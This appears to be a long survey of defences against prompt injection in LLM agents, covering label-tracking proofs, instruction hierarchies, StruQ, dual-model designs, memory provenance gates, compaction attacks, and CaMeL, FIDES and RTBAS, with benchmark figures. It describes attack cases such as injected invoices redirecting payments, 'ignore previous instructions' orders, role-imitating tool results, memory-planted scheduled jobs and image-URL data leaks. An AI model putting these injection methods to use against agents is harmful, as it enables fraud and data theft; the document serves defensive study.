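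Suppose the observer sees "paid" with probability 0.7 for one secret and 0.9 for another, and the remaining runs don't finish. The theorem allows this, because ω can give "paid" a probability of 0.9. A program can't produce "paid" with probability 0.7 for one secret and "refused" with probability 0.7 for the other, because the probabilities in ω would have to total 1.4. Garby and colleagues also show that the statistical distance between the two distributions, which measures how well anyone could tell them apart, is at most the average probability of not finishing. That limit is (0.3 + 0.1)/2 = 0.2 in the first example.

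The proof of the theorem uses a second way of running programs, which skips a computation as soon as the computation's label is no longer visible to the observer and uses a dummy value instead. The results can't depend on anything hidden from the observer, and these runs finish at least as often as the originals, so they supply the required ω.

The same argument works for integrity. Untrusted inputs can affect only results labelled U, unless the program contains an `endorse` command that relabels untrusted data as trusted. The second theorem covers programs with such commands. Endorsement weakens the integrity guarantee, but the confidentiality guarantee holds for any untrusted inputs and any use of `endorse`.

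A third theorem shows that the running interpreter's results follow the distribution in the mathematical definition, assuming that the model's replies follow fixed probabilities given the conversation. Lean 4, a proof assistant that checks every step of a proof mechanically, has verified all three theorems. The interpreter is also written in Lean and makes the calls to the model, so the proofs apply to the program that runs the agent. The proofs don't cover the network request to the model's provider, whether the source labels are true, or the choice of checks on each tool.

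### An agent that never obeys

Dongol avoids the strictness of noninterference by comparing each agent with a reference agent. Both follow the same plan, which is fixed before either reads anything untrusted, and the same monitor checks their tool calls. The reference agent reads untrusted content as data but never follows instructions in it. Its behaviour serves as the policy, so nobody has to write a separate one for each task.

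*Relativising Integrity and Robustness* (Dongol, 2026) uses this comparison to define relative integrity. Each run leaves an ordered record of its trusted inputs and its effects, such as payments. If two runs have the same trusted inputs but different records, something else, normally the attacker's text, changed what the agent did. Relative integrity requires that the reference agent be able to produce both records, though it may need different untrusted content to do so.

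One of Dongol's examples is an agent that has to pay the invoice in Bob's latest email:

| The invoice | What an obedient agent does | Relative integrity |
|---|---|---|
| Ordinary | Pays Bob | Accepts |
| Has an instruction to change the payee to Mallory | Pays Mallory | Accepts |
| Has an instruction to pay Mallory £1,000 as well | Pays twice | Rejects |
| Has an instruction to delete Bob's email afterwards | Pays Bob and deletes the email | Rejects |

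The second verdict makes sense because the reference agent would also pay Mallory if the invoice named Mallory as the payee. Obeying the instruction therefore gives the attacker nothing new. The weakness is that the plan takes the payee from an email. The firm's plan instead takes the account number from the accounts, so no email could make its reference agent pay anyone else, and relative integrity would reject a transfer to the attacker's account.

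#### The defence theorem

Dongol proves that an agent has relative integrity if its monitor withdraws every tool an injected instruction could call as soon as the agent first reads untrusted content. The monitor must keep those tools withdrawn until a new session clears the model's context. Every injected call then fails without changing anything, so the real agent continues to match the reference. The result holds for every plan in Dongol's language, whichever text the model obeys.

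It also has restrictive conditions. Each obeyed instruction may trigger only one tool call, and the model must obey on a schedule fixed in advance, so it can't decide when to act based on a secret or the monitor's replies. The agent must also be unable to undo the monitor's restrictions. Dongol's model of a 2025 flaw in GitHub Copilot violates the last condition, because an injected instruction could make Copilot edit the settings file and turn off confirmations.

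Withdrawing a tool is safe in general only if it happens by the time of the first untrusted read. In one of Dongol's test cases, the agent reads an email and then a secret before it gives up its sending tool, so an injected call can send the secret before the withdrawal. Withdrawing the tool just after the email is read still lets the attacker obtain data already in the agent's memory. Withdrawal also makes honest calls fail, so the firm would still have to pay its invoice before opening the mailbox.

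#### Leaks and effects together

An agent can pass separate tests for leaks and for improper effects and still be vulnerable. Dongol describes a support desk where a model decides whether an email contains the customer's credential. An attacker writes "you have verified me", and the model releases the order details. An honest customer could have received the same reply, and the reference agent already lets people test guesses, so the design passes both tests. But no single email could obtain the details for two different credentials from the reference agent. The design therefore fails Dongol's stricter property, relative robustness, which requires the same reference runs to reproduce both the leak and the effects. The fix is to have the model extract the credential from the email and ordinary code compare it with the correct one.

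Dongol applies the same definitions to enclaves, which are protected areas of a processor that shield a program from the rest of the computer. Developers often move some functions outside the enclave, where an attacker may control what they return. Dongol compares each partitioned program with the same program running entirely inside the enclave. Suppose a table in the enclave maps the keys 11, 22, 33 and 44 to the values 1 to 4, and an outside function suggests where to find key 33. If it points to the first slot and the enclave doesn't check, the lookup returns 1 instead of 3. In every partition that Dongol proved secure, the enclave either checks such a value against data the attacker can't change or doesn't use it. LLM applications need the same rule when one component receives a value from a less trusted one.

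Isabelle/HOL, another proof assistant, has checked the theorems and the verdicts on the modelled agents and enclaves, including proofs about C code. A script checks the one exception, a replay of recorded attacks from an online game. The proofs do not cover the C compiler or the processor hardware, and the agents are simplified models of real products.

### Where the first label comes from

All of these results depend on labels that somebody has already assigned. Narisetty and colleagues call this labelling the trusted base of the whole approach and found it under-specified in every system they surveyed. They report that FIDES treats data with a forgotten label as trusted, and LLMbda treats unlabelled values as trusted and public. Treating unlabelled data as untrusted would be safer but would block more legitimate work.

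Some sources that look trusted can contain data from outsiders. Dongol points out that a calendar is not a trusted source if outsiders can add invitations to it. The firm's accounts can have the same problem. If the bookkeeper copied an account number from a fraudulent email last month, the database will now supply it with a trusted label, and the proofs will still hold even though the number they protect is wrong.

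Most systems also give a trusted label to text that a user pastes from a stranger. But FIDES allows a different label for an individual message, so a chat program could mark pasted text as untrusted, although it would miss anything the user retyped.

### Endorsement as a planned exception

Endorsement makes room for context-dependent tasks, such as adding any meeting requests in the inbox to the calendar.

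One way to limit the risk is to endorse only answers from a short list. If a model without tools sorts an email into one of eight categories, the attacker controls at most log₂ 8 = 3 bits. Costa and colleagues apply this idea in their labels, which record whether a value is a yes-or-no answer, a choice from a list or free text. But the number of bits doesn't measure the possible damage, because one bit is enough to decide whether a payment is approved.

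Garby and colleagues tested endorsement with Randori, an agent written in LLMbda, on AgentDojo's banking suite. Two of 1,296 attacks succeeded. In both, the user had asked the agent to make whatever payment a text file specified, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. Without endorsement, the label checks block this attack, but they also block the same task when the file is genuine. With no attack present, removing endorsement reduced the tasks completed with one of the models, Qwen3.7-plus, from 36 to 30 out of 48 attempts.

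Randori's planning model writes its endorsements before it sees any untrusted data, so an injected instruction can't add more. But the model can still endorse more than it should. Other systems ask the user to endorse each action, which lets attackers try to deceive the user and, as Narisetty and colleagues note, leads to approval fatigue.

### Leaks through control flow and timing

CaMeL's developers also found side channels in their own system, where its behaviour can leak information even when no tool call contains the secret. Garby and colleagues describe another in the loop that restarts CaMeL after an error. Each attempt can reveal one bit of information by showing whether the security policy blocked it. An attacker can use the loop repeatedly because it sits outside the part of the system that tracks labels. A six-digit code would take about 20 attempts, since 2²⁰ is just over a million.

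LLMbda closes this gap by putting the retry loop inside the tracked program. *Ghost in the Agent* (2026) instead presents NeuroTaint, an offline auditor that searches for cases where the agent copied untrusted content or where that content affected a decision. NeuroTaint runs after the fact, so it can't prevent the leaks it finds.

Timing leaks are harder to rule out. In one of Dongol's examples, the user approves the exact text of a reply, and an injected instruction tells the agent to send private data instead. The monitor allows the injected call only if the private data is identical to the approved reply. In either case the attacker receives one message with the same text, but it arrives a step earlier if the two match. The agent is therefore secure only against an attacker who can't time the messages. Costa and colleagues leave timing out of their model.

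### Harm done by text alone

Checks on tool calls don't protect the user from a misleading answer. The attacker's email could make the assistant report that the supplier has changed banks and that someone should update the accounts, without any tool call breaking a rule. If the manager believes the summary and enters the new number, the assistant will treat that number as trusted the following week. An application could show the user which parts of an answer came from untrusted sources, but the theorems don't cover what people do with that information.

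Displaying a reply can leak private data. If the reply contains a web image, loading it sends a request to an outside server, and the image's address can carry the data. Dongol's theorems assume that displaying a reply has no effect the attacker can see, so the display software has to block such requests or send them through the monitor.

### What is left to trust

A proof with gaps like these can still greatly reduce what the firm has to trust. With no controls, its money depends on how the model reacts to every email anyone might send, which nobody can check. In LLMbda, a plan without endorsements can do only what the tool library permits, even if the model that wrote it is fully compromised. The firm would still have to check how the library labels the mailbox and the accounts, what the transfer tool requires, and where plans use `endorse`, but that review is manageable.

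Proofs can also rule out mistakes that a reviewer might overlook. Garby and colleagues found that in CaMeL, inserting an untrusted value into a piece of text silently made it trusted. Their theorems rule out this type of error in the LLMbda interpreter.

Developers can also use the assumptions as a checklist. Dongol's theorems require every tool call and every untrusted read to go through the monitor. A program like AgentDojo's meets both requirements because it checks each call itself before running it. An agent that retrieves memories from earlier sessions or uses a browser outside the monitor's control does not meet the assumptions, so the theorems do not show whether it is safe.

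## Experiments on context zones

All the proofs about labels assume a boundary between trusted and untrusted text. Developers have tried to draw that boundary in three places: inside one model's input, between separate models with separate inputs, and within the memory that an application keeps after a task ends. The location largely determines what enforces a zone's permissions. Inside one input, the model has to enforce the boundary, which it learns to do from training or from the prompt. Between separate inputs, ordinary code can control what crosses. In memory, either the model or code can enforce the boundary, but some current products draw it in code and then erase it.

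### Zones inside one input

The simplest way to create a context zone is to put a pair of markers around outside text and instruct the model to ignore any commands between them. Developers call this spotlighting. An attacker who can guess the closing marker can include a copy of it in an email, followed by text that appears to come from the user.

*StruQ* (Chen, Piet and colleagues, 2024) uses ordinary code to prevent outsiders from forging markers. The developer supplies the prompt and the data separately, and a front end joins them with reserved tokens that have no other use. The front end also deletes anything in the data that would turn into one of those tokens. It repeats the deletion until nothing changes, because removing one marker can join the two halves of another.

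The model still has to follow the markers, so Chen and colleagues fine-tuned Llama-7B and Mistral-7B to do so. They used ordinary examples of instructions and answers and left at least half of them unchanged. In up to a quarter, they added a second instruction to the data. In up to another quarter, they also put a fake answer before the added instruction to make the original task seem finished. The correct response always answered the prompt and ignored the added text.

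They then ran each attack on 208 examples, trying to make the model print "Hacked!". These are some of the attack success rates:

| Attack | Llama | Llama with StruQ | Mistral | Mistral with StruQ |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| An order to ignore previous instructions | 12% | 0% | 11% | 0% |
| A fake answer and a new instruction, using the real markers | 96% | 0% | 96% | 0% |
| Injections that another LLM tailors to each task | 97% | 9% | 100% | 36% |
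| Strings that an algorithm optimises against the model | 97% | 58% | 99% | 56% |

Markers that differed slightly from the real ones could pass the filter, but they worked in at most 1% of cases, so the training did contribute. The optimised strings also contained no genuine markers, so the filter could not stop them, and they got through the part of the defence that depends on the model.

The change had little effect on utility. GPT-4 compared each model's answers to 805 requests with those of a reference model. It preferred Llama's answers 67.2% of the time before the change and 67.6% after, and Mistral's 80.0% before and 78.7% after. Neither model had tools, however, so these results don't show whether StruQ would stop an unwanted payment.

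#### The instruction hierarchy

StruQ has two zones. The instruction hierarchy, which Eric Wallace and colleagues at OpenAI proposed later in 2024, ranks several, with system messages first, then user messages, then tool results. OpenAI has since added a developer level between the system and the user.

Guo, Ceron Uribe and colleagues (2026), in *IH-Challenge*, define the hierarchy as a shrinking set of acceptable responses. Let B₀ be all possible responses, and let Cᵢ be the responses that satisfy the instructions of the i-th role, counting down from the top. Then:

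Bᵢ = Bᵢ₋₁ ∩ Cᵢ if the two sets overlap, and Bᵢ = Bᵢ₋₁ if they don't

Suppose the system message requires approval for every transfer and a supplier's email requests one without approval. No response can satisfy both, so the assistant ignores the email's request. But if the user asks the assistant to pay an invoice and doesn't name an account, an email that names one conflicts with no other instruction, so the assistant follows it. The definition resolves conflicts between sources while still allowing tool results to contain valid instructions. *Training LLMs to Enforce Multi-Level Instruction Hierarchies via Gravity-Weighted Direct Preference Optimization* (2026) proposes a stricter five-level scheme in which tool output has no authority to give instructions.

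Guo and colleagues trained GPT-5-Mini on the hierarchy with reinforcement learning. For each task, an attacker model wrote a low-priority message, tested it and revised it within a fixed number of tries. A short Python program scored the result. The tasks were easy, such as never using a certain word, so that a failure would be due to the conflicting instructions rather than the difficulty of the task.

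Average robustness across 16 tests rose from 84.1% to 94.1%. It rose from 44% to 100% on OpenAI's internal set of prompt injections, which includes attempts to make an agent send malicious emails, but only from 88% to 91% on the public CyberSecEval 2 benchmark. The attacks in both sets are fixed. People who could refine their attacks still succeeded on 11.7% of tasks, down from 36.2%.

The training also made the model slightly less useful, lowering its win rate against OpenAI's older o1 model on typical chat requests from 71% to 66%. Part of the training set penalised needless refusals. Leaving that part out raised robustness slightly, from 94.1% to 95.7%, but lowered the model's helpfulness score on safety-related conversations from 77.3% to 61.3%. As with AgentDojo, a model can score well on security partly by refusing.

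#### How well models keep to the hierarchy

*IH-Benchmark* (McCauley, Kan and Martin, 2026) ran 32 model configurations through 2,323 conflict scenarios, five times each. In 1,824 of these, the rogue instruction arrived in a tool result. Another 365 scenarios had no conflict and checked whether the models could do the tasks. The scores weight each category of requirement equally, so they aren't simple shares of all cases.

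On average, the models upheld the system prompt against the user 84.6% of the time. At the boundary that matters for indirect injection, they resisted instructions in tool results only 69.6% of the time. Claude Opus 4.6 resisted all of these instructions, while Qwen 3 235B resisted 5.4%. Grok 4.20 scored 92.7% against users but 61.2% against tool results, which shows why developers need to test the two boundaries separately.

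Models also resisted some types of injected instruction more than others. They resisted 94.0% of orders to close other customers' support tickets and 86.8% of attempts to obtain another ticket's details, but only 45.4% when a tool result contained an instruction to misreport its contents. The firm's assistant might therefore refuse an obviously improper action and still give the manager a false summary.

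A warning in the system prompt helped some models. The average score against tool results was 63.4% with no warning, 69.3% with a short one and 76.2% with a detailed one. Grok 4.20 rose from 31.0% to 88.9%, but Qwen rose only from 5.4% to 5.5%. A developer who relies on such a warning has to retest it whenever the model changes.

Opus 4.6's perfect score covers four ways of presenting each injection, all fixed in advance. The model could also sometimes pass without finishing the user's task.

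*When Context Gets Root* (2026) describes an attack called ChatInject, in which a tool result imitates the formatting of a more privileged role. The paper also explains that models learn the significance of roles from ordinary training data, where people's chat logs mostly show system instructions being followed. Even when role labels are genuine, a model can give more internal weight to the lower-priority request, according to *Steering Instruction Hierarchies at Inference Time* (2026).

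Better training could improve all these numbers, but *Conflux* (Buckley and Schroeder de Witt, 2026) argues that it can't provide a guarantee. Two emails can have exactly the same text even though one comes from a colleague who is authorized to order payments and the other from an attacker. A deterministic rule that uses only the text must make the same decision for both, so it either permits the attacker's payment or blocks the colleague's. Software outside the model therefore has to supply the sender's identity. A developer can put the verified sender into the prompt, but the model may still ignore it.

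### Zones in separate contexts

*The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposed splitting an assistant into two models. The privileged model receives the user's request and can call tools, but never reads text from outside sources. The quarantined model reads that text and has no tools. Ordinary software stores the quarantined model's output in a variable and passes only the variable's name to the privileged model.

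To summarise the supplier emails, the privileged model could have the software pass `$EMAILS` to the quarantined model, store the result in `$SUMMARY` and show it to the user. An injected instruction could corrupt the summary, but it couldn't reach the model that controls the transfer tool. Code enforces this boundary, so it holds even if the quarantined model follows every injected instruction.

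A variable's contents can still do harm, for instance if the plan takes an account number from an email. Willison later acknowledged a flaw in the pattern and welcomed CaMeL, which addresses the flaw by also checking the data that goes into each step.

Willison reported no attack success rate or utility for the pattern, and expected it to make assistants more complicated to build and less pleasant to use. The pattern also trusts any text the user pastes. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents* (2025) worked through ten applications, from simple operating-system assistants to software engineering agents, to show how developers could use such patterns. These case studies are design exercises and don't measure attack success or utility.

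Developers can also put the boundary between apps. IsolateGPT, which Yuhao Wu, Franziska Roesner and colleagues first released in 2024 as SecGPT, runs each third-party app in its own isolated environment with its own model. A central hub chooses the app for each request, and apps can communicate only through the hub. Wu and colleagues reported that isolation stopped a number of attacks without any loss of functionality, and that it added less than 30% to the running time for three-quarters of the queries they tested. But isolation doesn't protect an app from text the app itself reads. If a mail app can both read and send messages, instructions injected into an email could still make it send one.

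#### Permissions that shrink as text crosses

Conflux, by Buckley and Schroeder de Witt, lets text from anyone enter a context, so contexts don't have to be isolated from each other. It records each context's principals, meaning the people or agents whose information has gone into that context, and permits an action only if every principal may perform it under the organisation's existing access rules.

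The assistant would keep its permission to make transfers after reading an email from the firm's bookkeeper, who is allowed to make payments, but would lose it after reading one from a supplier, because suppliers can't order transfers from the firm's account. This resembles Biba's low-water-mark rule, but Conflux keeps the identities of everyone involved instead of a single trust level.

The record has to be complete. A bookkeeper who copies an attacker's text into the firm's own files can defeat it, just as they can defeat a label. An attacker who controls a mail gateway could also influence a decision by withholding one message and delivering another, without writing either. Even with a perfect record, the basic rule checks only the type of action, not whether a payment goes to the right account. Buckley and Schroeder de Witt leave that check to separate policies.

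The record-keeping was tested on 351 symbolic scenarios, without a language model. Of these, 208 were legitimate tasks the software should allow, 95 were tasks it should block, and 48 were vulnerable to an attack.

| Who goes on the record | Mean number of principals | Legitimate tasks completed | Vulnerable cases exploited |
|---|---|---|---|
| Only the person making the request | 1.00 | 208 of 208 | 48 of 48 |
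| Everyone who may have written the data | 8.62 | 173 of 208 | 0 of 48 |
| Authenticated authors | 3.08 | 208 of 208 | 0 of 48 |

The rule blocked about one in six legitimate tasks when authorship was guessed cautiously, and none when it was authenticated. The scenarios don't show how often a real application would know who wrote the text in its context. Buckley and Schroeder de Witt also ran Conflux on AgentDojo, but those runs only read data and never attempted an action that the rule could have blocked, so they provide no attack success rate or utility for the defence.

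### Zones in memory

An injected instruction does more damage if the application saves it. Schwarz's *Countermind* proposes memory zones that would separate small talk, which gets very few rights, from code under analysis. Information could move between zones only with explicit authorisation. The model would use only the latest validated version of its memory, so if an attacker's claim about approvals got into memory, the previous rules would stay in force until the new version passed validation.

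Schwarz also describes a monitor for gradual changes, such as the harmless term "Admin-Panel" becoming associated with privileged commands. This design has not yet been tested. Its validation step would have to detect a poisoned update, which is as hard as detecting a poisoned email unless the software also has a record of where the update came from.

In *Sleeper Channels and Provenance Gates*, Maloyan and Namiot (2026) studied attacks that are stored in an agent's memory and take effect later. They focused on OpenClaw, an agent that runs continuously on its owner's computer. In their main example, an attacker emails a tip about a daily health check, with a web address in the email, and the agent saves a note about it. Days later, the owner asks the agent to set up the health check from the email. The agent creates a scheduled job that reports to the attacker's address and keeps running without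 further action from the attacker.

OpenClaw puts markers around outside text and adds a security warning, so only the prompt enforces this zone. Maloyan and Namiot gave an unnamed frontier-class reasoning model the saved note with the markers and warning. The model created the attacker's job in 19 of 20 trials, and in 7 of 10 trials of a two-stage version. The trials cover only one scenario, in which the owner had asked for the job described in the email. A model can't carry out that request and also reject every detail that came from outside.

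The provenance gate uses code to decide whether an action can go ahead. Each saved item keeps a record of all its sources, even after a model has summarised it. The gate refuses consequential actions that draw on an untrusted source, unless the owner endorses that exact action through a separate channel that the model can't write to. As in FIDES, each tool call inherits the origins of everything in the model's context, so rephrasing the attacker's text doesn't hide where it came from. The gate would also block a genuine health check prompted by an outsider's email until the owner approved it.

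The software has 42 tests, but 13 just confirm that OpenClaw's source code contains the lines the argument relies on. Only six run the gate in a simulated or adapted version of the agent, where it denied the attacker's job and allowed one that came entirely from the owner. The adapted version covers five of the ten places where the full design would intercept the agent. Maloyan and Namiot plan to measure attack success and utility but haven't reported any results for either.

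#### When the software summarises a long context

When a session approaches the model's context limit, the agent's software has a model summarise the earlier turns and continues from the summary, a process called compaction. The summary can mix the user's words with text from documents and attackers. Under Maloyan and Namiot's design, the summary would inherit the sources of everything it covers.

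In *LLM Agent Authorization Across Context Compaction*, Fei, Fei and colleagues (2026) recorded 1,108 automatic compactions in two coding agents, Anthropic's Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex. Each time, the software inserted the resulting summary as a user message, so text from an untrusted zone gained the user's authority without anyone endorsing it.

Summarising an agent's context (compaction) can undermine a defence even when code enforces it correctly. In Progent, a model turns the user's request into a list of permitted tool calls, and ordinary software blocks all other calls. Fei and colleagues had Progent write a new list for each request, because the agent completed 41 of 60 follow-up tasks that way and only 7 with a list fixed at the start. They then tested it on AgentDojo, with GPT-4o mini as both the agent and the summariser. After compaction, attacks that Progent had blocked succeeded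 in 31 of 100 cases, compared with 33 for an agent with no defence. The software still enforced the list, but the list now often included the attacker's transfer.

The results depended on whether the summary appeared as a user message or a tool result. Progent's list allowed the attacker's transfer in 17 of 30 banking runs when the summary was a user message, but in none of 28 runs when the same text was a tool result. With Spotlighting, the agent made the attacker's transfer in 34 of 64 runs when the summary was a user message, and in 5 of 64 when it was marked as a tool result.

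#### Better summaries don't solve the problem

More capable models write safer summaries when the attack is an instruction. GPT-5.4 mini and GPT-5.5 flagged the injection in 219 of the 220 summaries that kept the attacker's identifier, such as an account number. They rarely flagged an account number that the attacker presented as ordinary data.

Fei and colleagues tested this with a case much like the supplier email. The user gives the landlord's account number and asks what a notice says. The notice, which the attacker wrote, contains a different number but no instruction. After compaction, the user asks the agent to pay the rent. Permissions based on the summary allowed a payment to the attacker's account in 290 of 320 cases. When GPT-5.5 wrote the permissions, they still allowed it in 59% of cases. Permissions based on the user's own messages never allowed it.

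They also proved a limit on any system that reads text without a record of who wrote it. Let p_L be the probability that the system permits an action based on a legitimate record, and p_A the probability for a forged one. Then:

p_L − p_A ≤ TV(P_L, P_A)

The right-hand side is the total variation distance between the two kinds of input, which is 0 if they are indistinguishable and 1 if they never overlap. If the distance is 0.1, a system that accepts 95% of legitimate notices must accept at least 85% of forged ones. If the imitation is perfect, the system accepts both equally often, however good the summariser is.

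#### Separate inputs for the agent and its permissions

The remedy is to withhold the summary from the model that writes the permissions while still letting the agent read it. The software attaches a cryptographic code to each user message when it arrives and copies the message unchanged through every compaction. Before the next request, a gate checks that the messages are genuine, complete and in order, then passes only those messages to the model that writes the permissions. If a check fails, the agent gets no permissions.

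Fei and colleagues compared several arrangements on 40 AgentDojo runs that contained attacks:

| Source of the permissions | What the agent reads | Attacks completed | User tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Summary | Summary as a user message | 7 | 9 |
| Latest user message | Summary as a tool result | 0 | 18 |
| All user messages, through the gate | Summary as a user message | 0 | 13 |
| All user messages, through the gate | Summary as a tool result | 0 | 19 |
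| All user messages, through the gate | User messages only | 1 | 26 |
| User's request, no compaction | Full transcript | 2 | 27 |

The one attack that got past the gate had also succeeded without compaction. In these runs, relabelling the summary as a tool result helped nearly as much as the gate. The rent case shows a limit of relabelling. The landlord's account number was in an earlier message, so permissions based only on the latest message left the recipient unrestricted in every session. With the gate, GPT-5.4 mini tried to pay the attacker 34 times in 80 runs, and the software blocked every attempt.

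The checks take less than half a millisecond per request, so speed is no obstacle. Codex already uses a simpler fix. Since October 2026, its safety reviewer has attributed summaries to the assistant instead of the user. This may be enough while the messages stay inside one program. But if the agent can edit the saved session, it can insert a fake user message, which the cryptographic codes would expose.

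The gate still treats text that the user pastes as the user's own. It also can't choose between accounts when the user leaves that choice to a document. In 6 of the 40 runs with the gate and the summary as a tool result, the permissions would have allowed the attacker's action because the user's request didn't specify a recipient. The attacks in those runs failed because of the agent's behaviour, not the boundary. The software would need to authenticate the document's source to close that gap in code.

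## Experiments on provenance tracking

A system that tracks provenance labels data when fetching it, copies the label to anything derived from that data, and checks the label before running a tool. The survey *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026) lists what the record of a tool call needs to contain: the tool and its input format, the values passed to it, the result, and whatever used that result later.

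If a model's reply takes the combined trust label of its whole context, a single untrusted email makes every later step untrusted. The main systems from 2025 avoid this either by keeping untrusted text away from the planning model or by estimating which text matters for the next step.

### CaMeL: labels on the values in a program

CaMeL, which Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues built at Google DeepMind in 2025, adds labels to the dual LLM pattern that Willison proposed. It would handle the firm's request in four steps:

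1. The privileged model, which sees only the user's request, writes the whole job as a program in a restricted form of Python.
2. An interpreter runs the program line by line. When a line fetches the emails, the interpreter stores them in a variable with a label recording their source.
3. If the program needs information from the emails, it sends them to the quarantined model. The answer comes back in a fixed structure, such as a list of client names, and keeps the emails' label.
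4. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs that tool's policy, which is a Python function. The function inspects the call and its arguments, then returns either permission or a refusal with a reason.

The program might look like this:

```
invoice = find_invoice("Acme Ltd")
emails = get_emails("this week")
summary = quarantined_llm("Summarise these", emails)
send_money(invoice.account, invoice.amount)
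```

The policy for transfers could require every source of the account number to be on a short list:

```
def check_transfer(account, amount):
    if account.sources <= {"user", "accounts"}:
        return allow()
    return deny("account number from an untrusted source")
```

The transfer in this program uses the account number on file, so the policy allows it. If the user had asked the assistant to pay the account named in the email, the number would carry the email's label and the policy would block the call. According to TechSpot, the interpreter can ask the user to confirm such a call instead of blocking it.

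These policies check one call at a time. *CaMeLoT* (2026) argues that they can't naturally express rules about a whole run, such as that the assistant must send a receipt at some point after every payment. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) criticises the choice of Python, with its dynamic types and exceptions, and recommends a purpose-built language with bounded loops and explicit conditions.

#### How much work CaMeL still gets done

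*Treating the Model as an Untrusted Component* (Aljumaily, Alseelawi and Alshabandar, 2026) reports that CaMeL solved 77% of AgentDojo's tasks in its original evaluation, compared with 84% for an undefended system. CaMeL also used about 2.8 times as many input tokens. A seven-point loss would be small for a defence that doesn't depend on the model's judgement, but other teams have measured larger losses.

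In *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL on AgentDojo's banking suite to compare it with their own agent. CaMeL completed 37.5% of the tasks with its policies on. It completed about twice as many with the policies off, but some injections then succeeded.

*PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) reran CaMeL on all of AgentDojo with three newer models. CaMeL completed 35% of the tasks with Qwen-3.8-27B, 60% with DeepSeek-V4-Flash and 57% with gpt-5.6-luna, 16 to 27 points below the undefended agents. The most effective type of attack succeeded in 0.3%, 28% and 36% of cases respectively. The last two rates are surprisingly high for a design in which injected text can't add a tool call. They may be due to looser policies or to how the rerun scored attacks.

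CaMeL did much worse on AgentDyn, a benchmark of more open-ended tasks. It completed none of the tasks with two of the models and under 4% with the third, while the undefended agents completed 63% to 75%. A program written before anyone has read the documents probably can't adapt to what is in them.

### FIDES: labels on the fields of a tool result

The planning model in FIDES, by Costa and colleagues, chooses one step at a time rather than having to commit to a whole program in advance. It can see any data that is as trustworthy as the conversation so far. Each field of a tool result can have its own label, so an email's authenticated sender address might be trusted while its subject and body are not. When a result arrives, FIDES moves a field into a variable only if that field would lower the context's trust level. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) treats both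 FIDES and CaMeL as versions of the dual LLM pattern.

One of AgentDojo's banking tasks shows the benefit of labelling fields separately. The user asks the agent to change a password if there has been a suspicious transaction. The agent saw the trusted amounts and dates, while the descriptions, which outsiders can write, stayed in variables. It judged one large payment suspicious from the amount alone. Because the context had remained trusted, the policy allowed the agent to change the password.

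Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo with GPT-4o. An ordinary agent without label checks carried out 152 injections, and FIDES with its checks switched off carried out 21. With the checks on, neither agent carried out any. The checks therefore provide the guarantee, and the variables recover some of the work that the checks would otherwise block:

| Share of tasks completed, no attack | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
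|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no checks | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Ordinary agent, label checks on | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES, label checks off | 63.5% | 50.0% | 65.0% | 63.8% |
| FIDES, label checks on | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

Costa and colleagues emphasise that FIDES completes 8 percentage points more tasks than the ordinary agent under the same checks. Compared with an unprotected agent, however, average completion across the four suites falls from 84% to 50%. Some of that loss came from GPT-4o's difficulty with variables, whose names it sometimes confused. Switching to OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model, raised FIDES's completion rate on the travel suite from 41% to 68%.

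The type of task explains much of the rest. In about 43% of the banking and Slack tasks, the right tool calls depend on what the data contains, compared with 5% in the workspace suite and 10% in travel. In many banking tasks, the agent has to do what a file specifies, and label checks block this unless it is endorsed. This probably also explains CaMeL's poor result on the banking suite.

The result of zero successful attacks depends on how Costa and colleagues assigned the labels. They marked a field as untrusted if any AgentDojo attack targets it. This gives a clear baseline, but the developer of a real application doesn't have a list of the places where attackers will write.

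### RTBAS: labels on parts of the conversation

Zhong, Chen and colleagues (2025), in *RTBAS*, leave untrusted text in the conversation and decide before each step whether the model needs it. They divide the history into regions, each with its own label. A region can be a whole message or one part of it. The process works as follows:

1. A screener picks out the regions that matter for the next step.
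2. The software combines the labels of those regions.
3. It hides every region whose label is more restrictive than the combined one.
4. The model writes its tool call from what remains.
5. The software compares the combined label with the tool's policy, and asks the user before running a call that the policy doesn't allow.

The third step limits the damage from a bad screener. If the screener leaves out a supplier's email, the email never reaches the model. If it includes the email unnecessarily, the payment needs the user's approval. Both mistakes make the system less useful but not less secure. However, the screener also processes the attacker's text, so an attacker may be able to influence what it hides.

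Zhong and colleagues built two screeners. One is a second language model that identifies the relevant regions. The other uses a small open model to measure how strongly each region affects the output, then passes those scores to a classifier, which reached 81% accuracy in offline tests.

On AgentDojo with GPT-4o, both versions of RTBAS blocked every attack that violated the policy. In one workspace case, RTBAS didn't track the possible injection because it was in text the user wrote, which was labeled trusted. With no attack present, utility fell by 10 points with the language-model screener and 7.4 with the classifier. Utility fell most in the Slack suite, to 22% and 33%, because its tasks often involve reading a website and acting on it. In these tests, the software automatically refused every suspicious call, so a user who could approve some of them would get more done.

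The language-model version of the screening more than doubled the average tokens and time per task on the banking suite, from about 2,700 to 5,850 tokens and from 4.4 to 9.7 seconds.

RTBAS is also designed to ask for approval less often. In 37 tasks involving private data, RTBAS with the language-model screener asked unnecessarily in 3, compared with 11 for a system that asks about every call. But it failed to ask in 4 tasks where it should have. Another weakness is that RTBAS treats unlabelled regions as trusted and public by default.

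The three systems differ mainly in what they label and what the planning model gets to see:

| | CaMeL | FIDES | RTBAS |
|---|---|---|---|
| What carries the label | Each value in the program | Each message and field of a tool result | Each region of the conversation |
| Untrusted text | Never reaches the planning model | Goes into variables, which the planner can open at the cost of its trust level | Visible only if the screener considers it relevant |
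| Planning | One program, written in advance | Step by step | Step by step |
| Utility in the developers' tests, no attack | 77%, against 84% undefended | 50%, against 84% (mean of four suites) | 7 to 10 points below undefended |

The last row doesn't rank them, because the models and policies differed.

### Labels on single arguments

Suppose a user asks an agent to summarise a web page and email the summary to their boss. The page has to influence the body of the email but should not influence the recipient. Fan, Li and colleagues (2026) argue in *The Granularity Mismatch in Agent Security* that a defence that makes one decision about the whole tool call can't handle this, because it either blocks a legitimate email or lets the page redirect it.

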